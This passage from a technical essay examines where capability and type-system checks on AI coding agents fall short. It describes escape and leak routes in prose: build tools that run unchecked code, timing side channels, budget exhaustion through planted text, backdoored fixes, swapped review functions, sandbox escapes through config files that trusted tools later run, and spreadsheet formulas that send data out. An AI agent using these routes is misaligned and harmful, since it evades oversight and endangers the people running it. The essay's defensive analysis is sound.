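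Developers can reduce this risk by granting narrower permissions. The type system will enforce the permissions they choose, but it can't determine which ones a task needs. In the price update, the agent could finish the job with either a function that only changes prices in one file or permission to write anywhere in the shop's folder, but the function is safer. For payments, even the permission the task requires is dangerous, so the owner also needs a limit on the amount or a list of approved accounts.

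### Commands, timing and runaway programs

External commands remain a gap because Scala's rules don't apply inside them. TACIT returns a command's output as ordinary text, so an agent that could run `cat`, which prints a file, could read the credentials without a `Classified` container. lampepfl offers a strict mode that blocks file commands such as `cat`, but an agent could still read the file through a general-purpose program such as `python` if the operator allows it. An example in TACIT's own interface requests permission to run `python`.

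Odersky and colleagues list `sbt`, a build tool for Scala, among the safe commands that an operator might allow. But `sbt` runs code from the project's build files, so an agent that can edit those files and start `sbt` can run code that TACIT never checked. This makes `sbt` a poor choice unless the agent can't edit the build files or `sbt` runs in a sandbox. An honest model is more likely to cause a smaller accident, such as deleting unsaved work by using the wrong option. Steering and sabotage make the problem much worse, because an attacker can look for a permitted command that runs others.

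Code can leak secrets through its timing without performing any forbidden operation. Suppose a function inside `map` counts to a billion if the first bit of a key is 1, and finishes immediately otherwise. The function is pure, so the compiler accepts it, and its result stays in a container. But whoever runs the cloud model can see how long the snippet took and learn that bit. Repeating this with a different bit each time would reveal the whole key, as with CaMeL's retry loop. Odersky and colleagues say they don't cover such channels.

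A mistake is unlikely to leak much through timing, since nobody would be measuring the delays. An outside attacker would have to plant the instructions and also measure the delay, for example by having the snippet contact the attacker's website before and after it. A dishonest provider could do both easily, so timing is mainly a concern for people who fear sabotage. An operator could hide the differences in timing by returning every result after the same delay, but every step would then take as long as the slowest one.

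Programs can also use too much time, memory or money, especially in LACUNA, where the model's code can call the model again. Zhao and colleagues note that a difficult task and an endless loop can look the same from outside. In their research test, they stopped nesting at 128 levels and ended each question after ten minutes. The time limit mattered because a depth limit does little to control the total number of calls. If every call makes two more, the twentieth level alone has about a million calls.

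Even an honest mistake can cause a runaway program, so everyone who uses such a system needs limits on time and spending. Steering and sabotage make those limits harder to set. An attacker who wants to stop the price updates only has to make the agent use up its budget, perhaps by planting text that leads it to keep writing code that won't compile. A higher limit gives the agent more time to recover but lets the attacker waste more of the owner's money.

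### Code that runs after the check

TACIT's SWE-bench test also shows that its checks don't cover the code an agent delivers. The agent had to repair real projects written mostly in Python. The compiler checked the Scala snippets the agent used to read and edit files, but not the repairs. About 125 of the 300 repairs passed their projects' tests, and any of them could have contained a vulnerability or a backdoor without breaking TACIT's rules.

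Mistakes are the most common problem in delivered code, and tests or reviewers can find some of them. Hostile inputs and sabotage can do more damage, because the code may later run on a machine with far more access than the agent had.

LACUNA can apply its limits to some code that is kept and reused. A programmer can ask the model for a function instead of a single answer, and the program can then reuse that function without calling the model again. When the model writes the function, the compiler checks it, including which capabilities it may use. The shop could run its nightly update this way if the surrounding program were written in Scala.

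Reuse also makes a bad function more harmful. In a long LACUNA session, an agent can replace a shared function with a new one of the same name and type, and later calls will use the new version. Zhao and colleagues present this as a way for agents to improve their own skills. But a function that reviews code changes has the same type whether it looks for flaws or approves everything. A bad replacement from an honest model is one more bug to find and fix, but a steered or hostile model could use one replacement to weaken every later review.

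### Files that a trusted program reads later

An agent can get code to run outside its sandbox without writing anything that looks like a program. In *The Week of Sandbox Escapes*, Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel (2026) describe seven ways around the limits on the coding agents Cursor, Codex, Gemini CLI and Antigravity. The three work for Pillar Security, which sells protection for machines that run such agents. In almost every case, the agent could stay inside its sandbox and write something that a trusted program outside would later run, load or treat as safe.

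Several of the findings, like the Miasma worm, relied on project files that can start programs. If a sandbox lets the agent write anywhere in the project, the agent can therefore choose what some of the developer's other tools will do, with all the access those tools have. Other findings involved background services that could do things the agent was not allowed to do, and a permitted Git command that could do more than its name suggested.

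The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them* reports that text planted in, for example, a README or a bug report triggered the escapes. Vendors fixed the flaws in Cursor and Codex. Google didn't patch the two in Antigravity, which it classed as hard to exploit, partly because the developer first has to trust a malicious project. That is a weak reason to leave them open, since developers routinely open strangers' projects.

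Planted text that steers the model makes this gap worse than mistakes do. A model might damage a settings file by accident, but it is unlikely to accidentally write one that starts an attacker's program. A sabotaged model could write such a file without any planted text, and could do so days before the developer opens the tool that uses it.

The same route exists under TACIT if the agent has permission to write to the whole project. The compiler treats a settings file as ordinary text, so it allows the agent to write one. Cohen and colleagues recommend asking for approval before an agent creates or changes a file that can start programs, running the tools that read such files under the same limits as the agent, and recording which files the agent wrote. TACIT's operator can also limit the agent to files that no other program will execute.

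Even the price file could be used to leak data. Spreadsheet programs can treat a cell that begins with an equals sign as a formula, and some formulas can send data to a website when someone opens the file. An agent that can add any text to `prices.csv` could write such a formula. The shop could prevent this by replacing the agent's general write permission with a function that accepts only a product already on the list and a number. The agent could still record the wrong price, but it could no longer add a formula.
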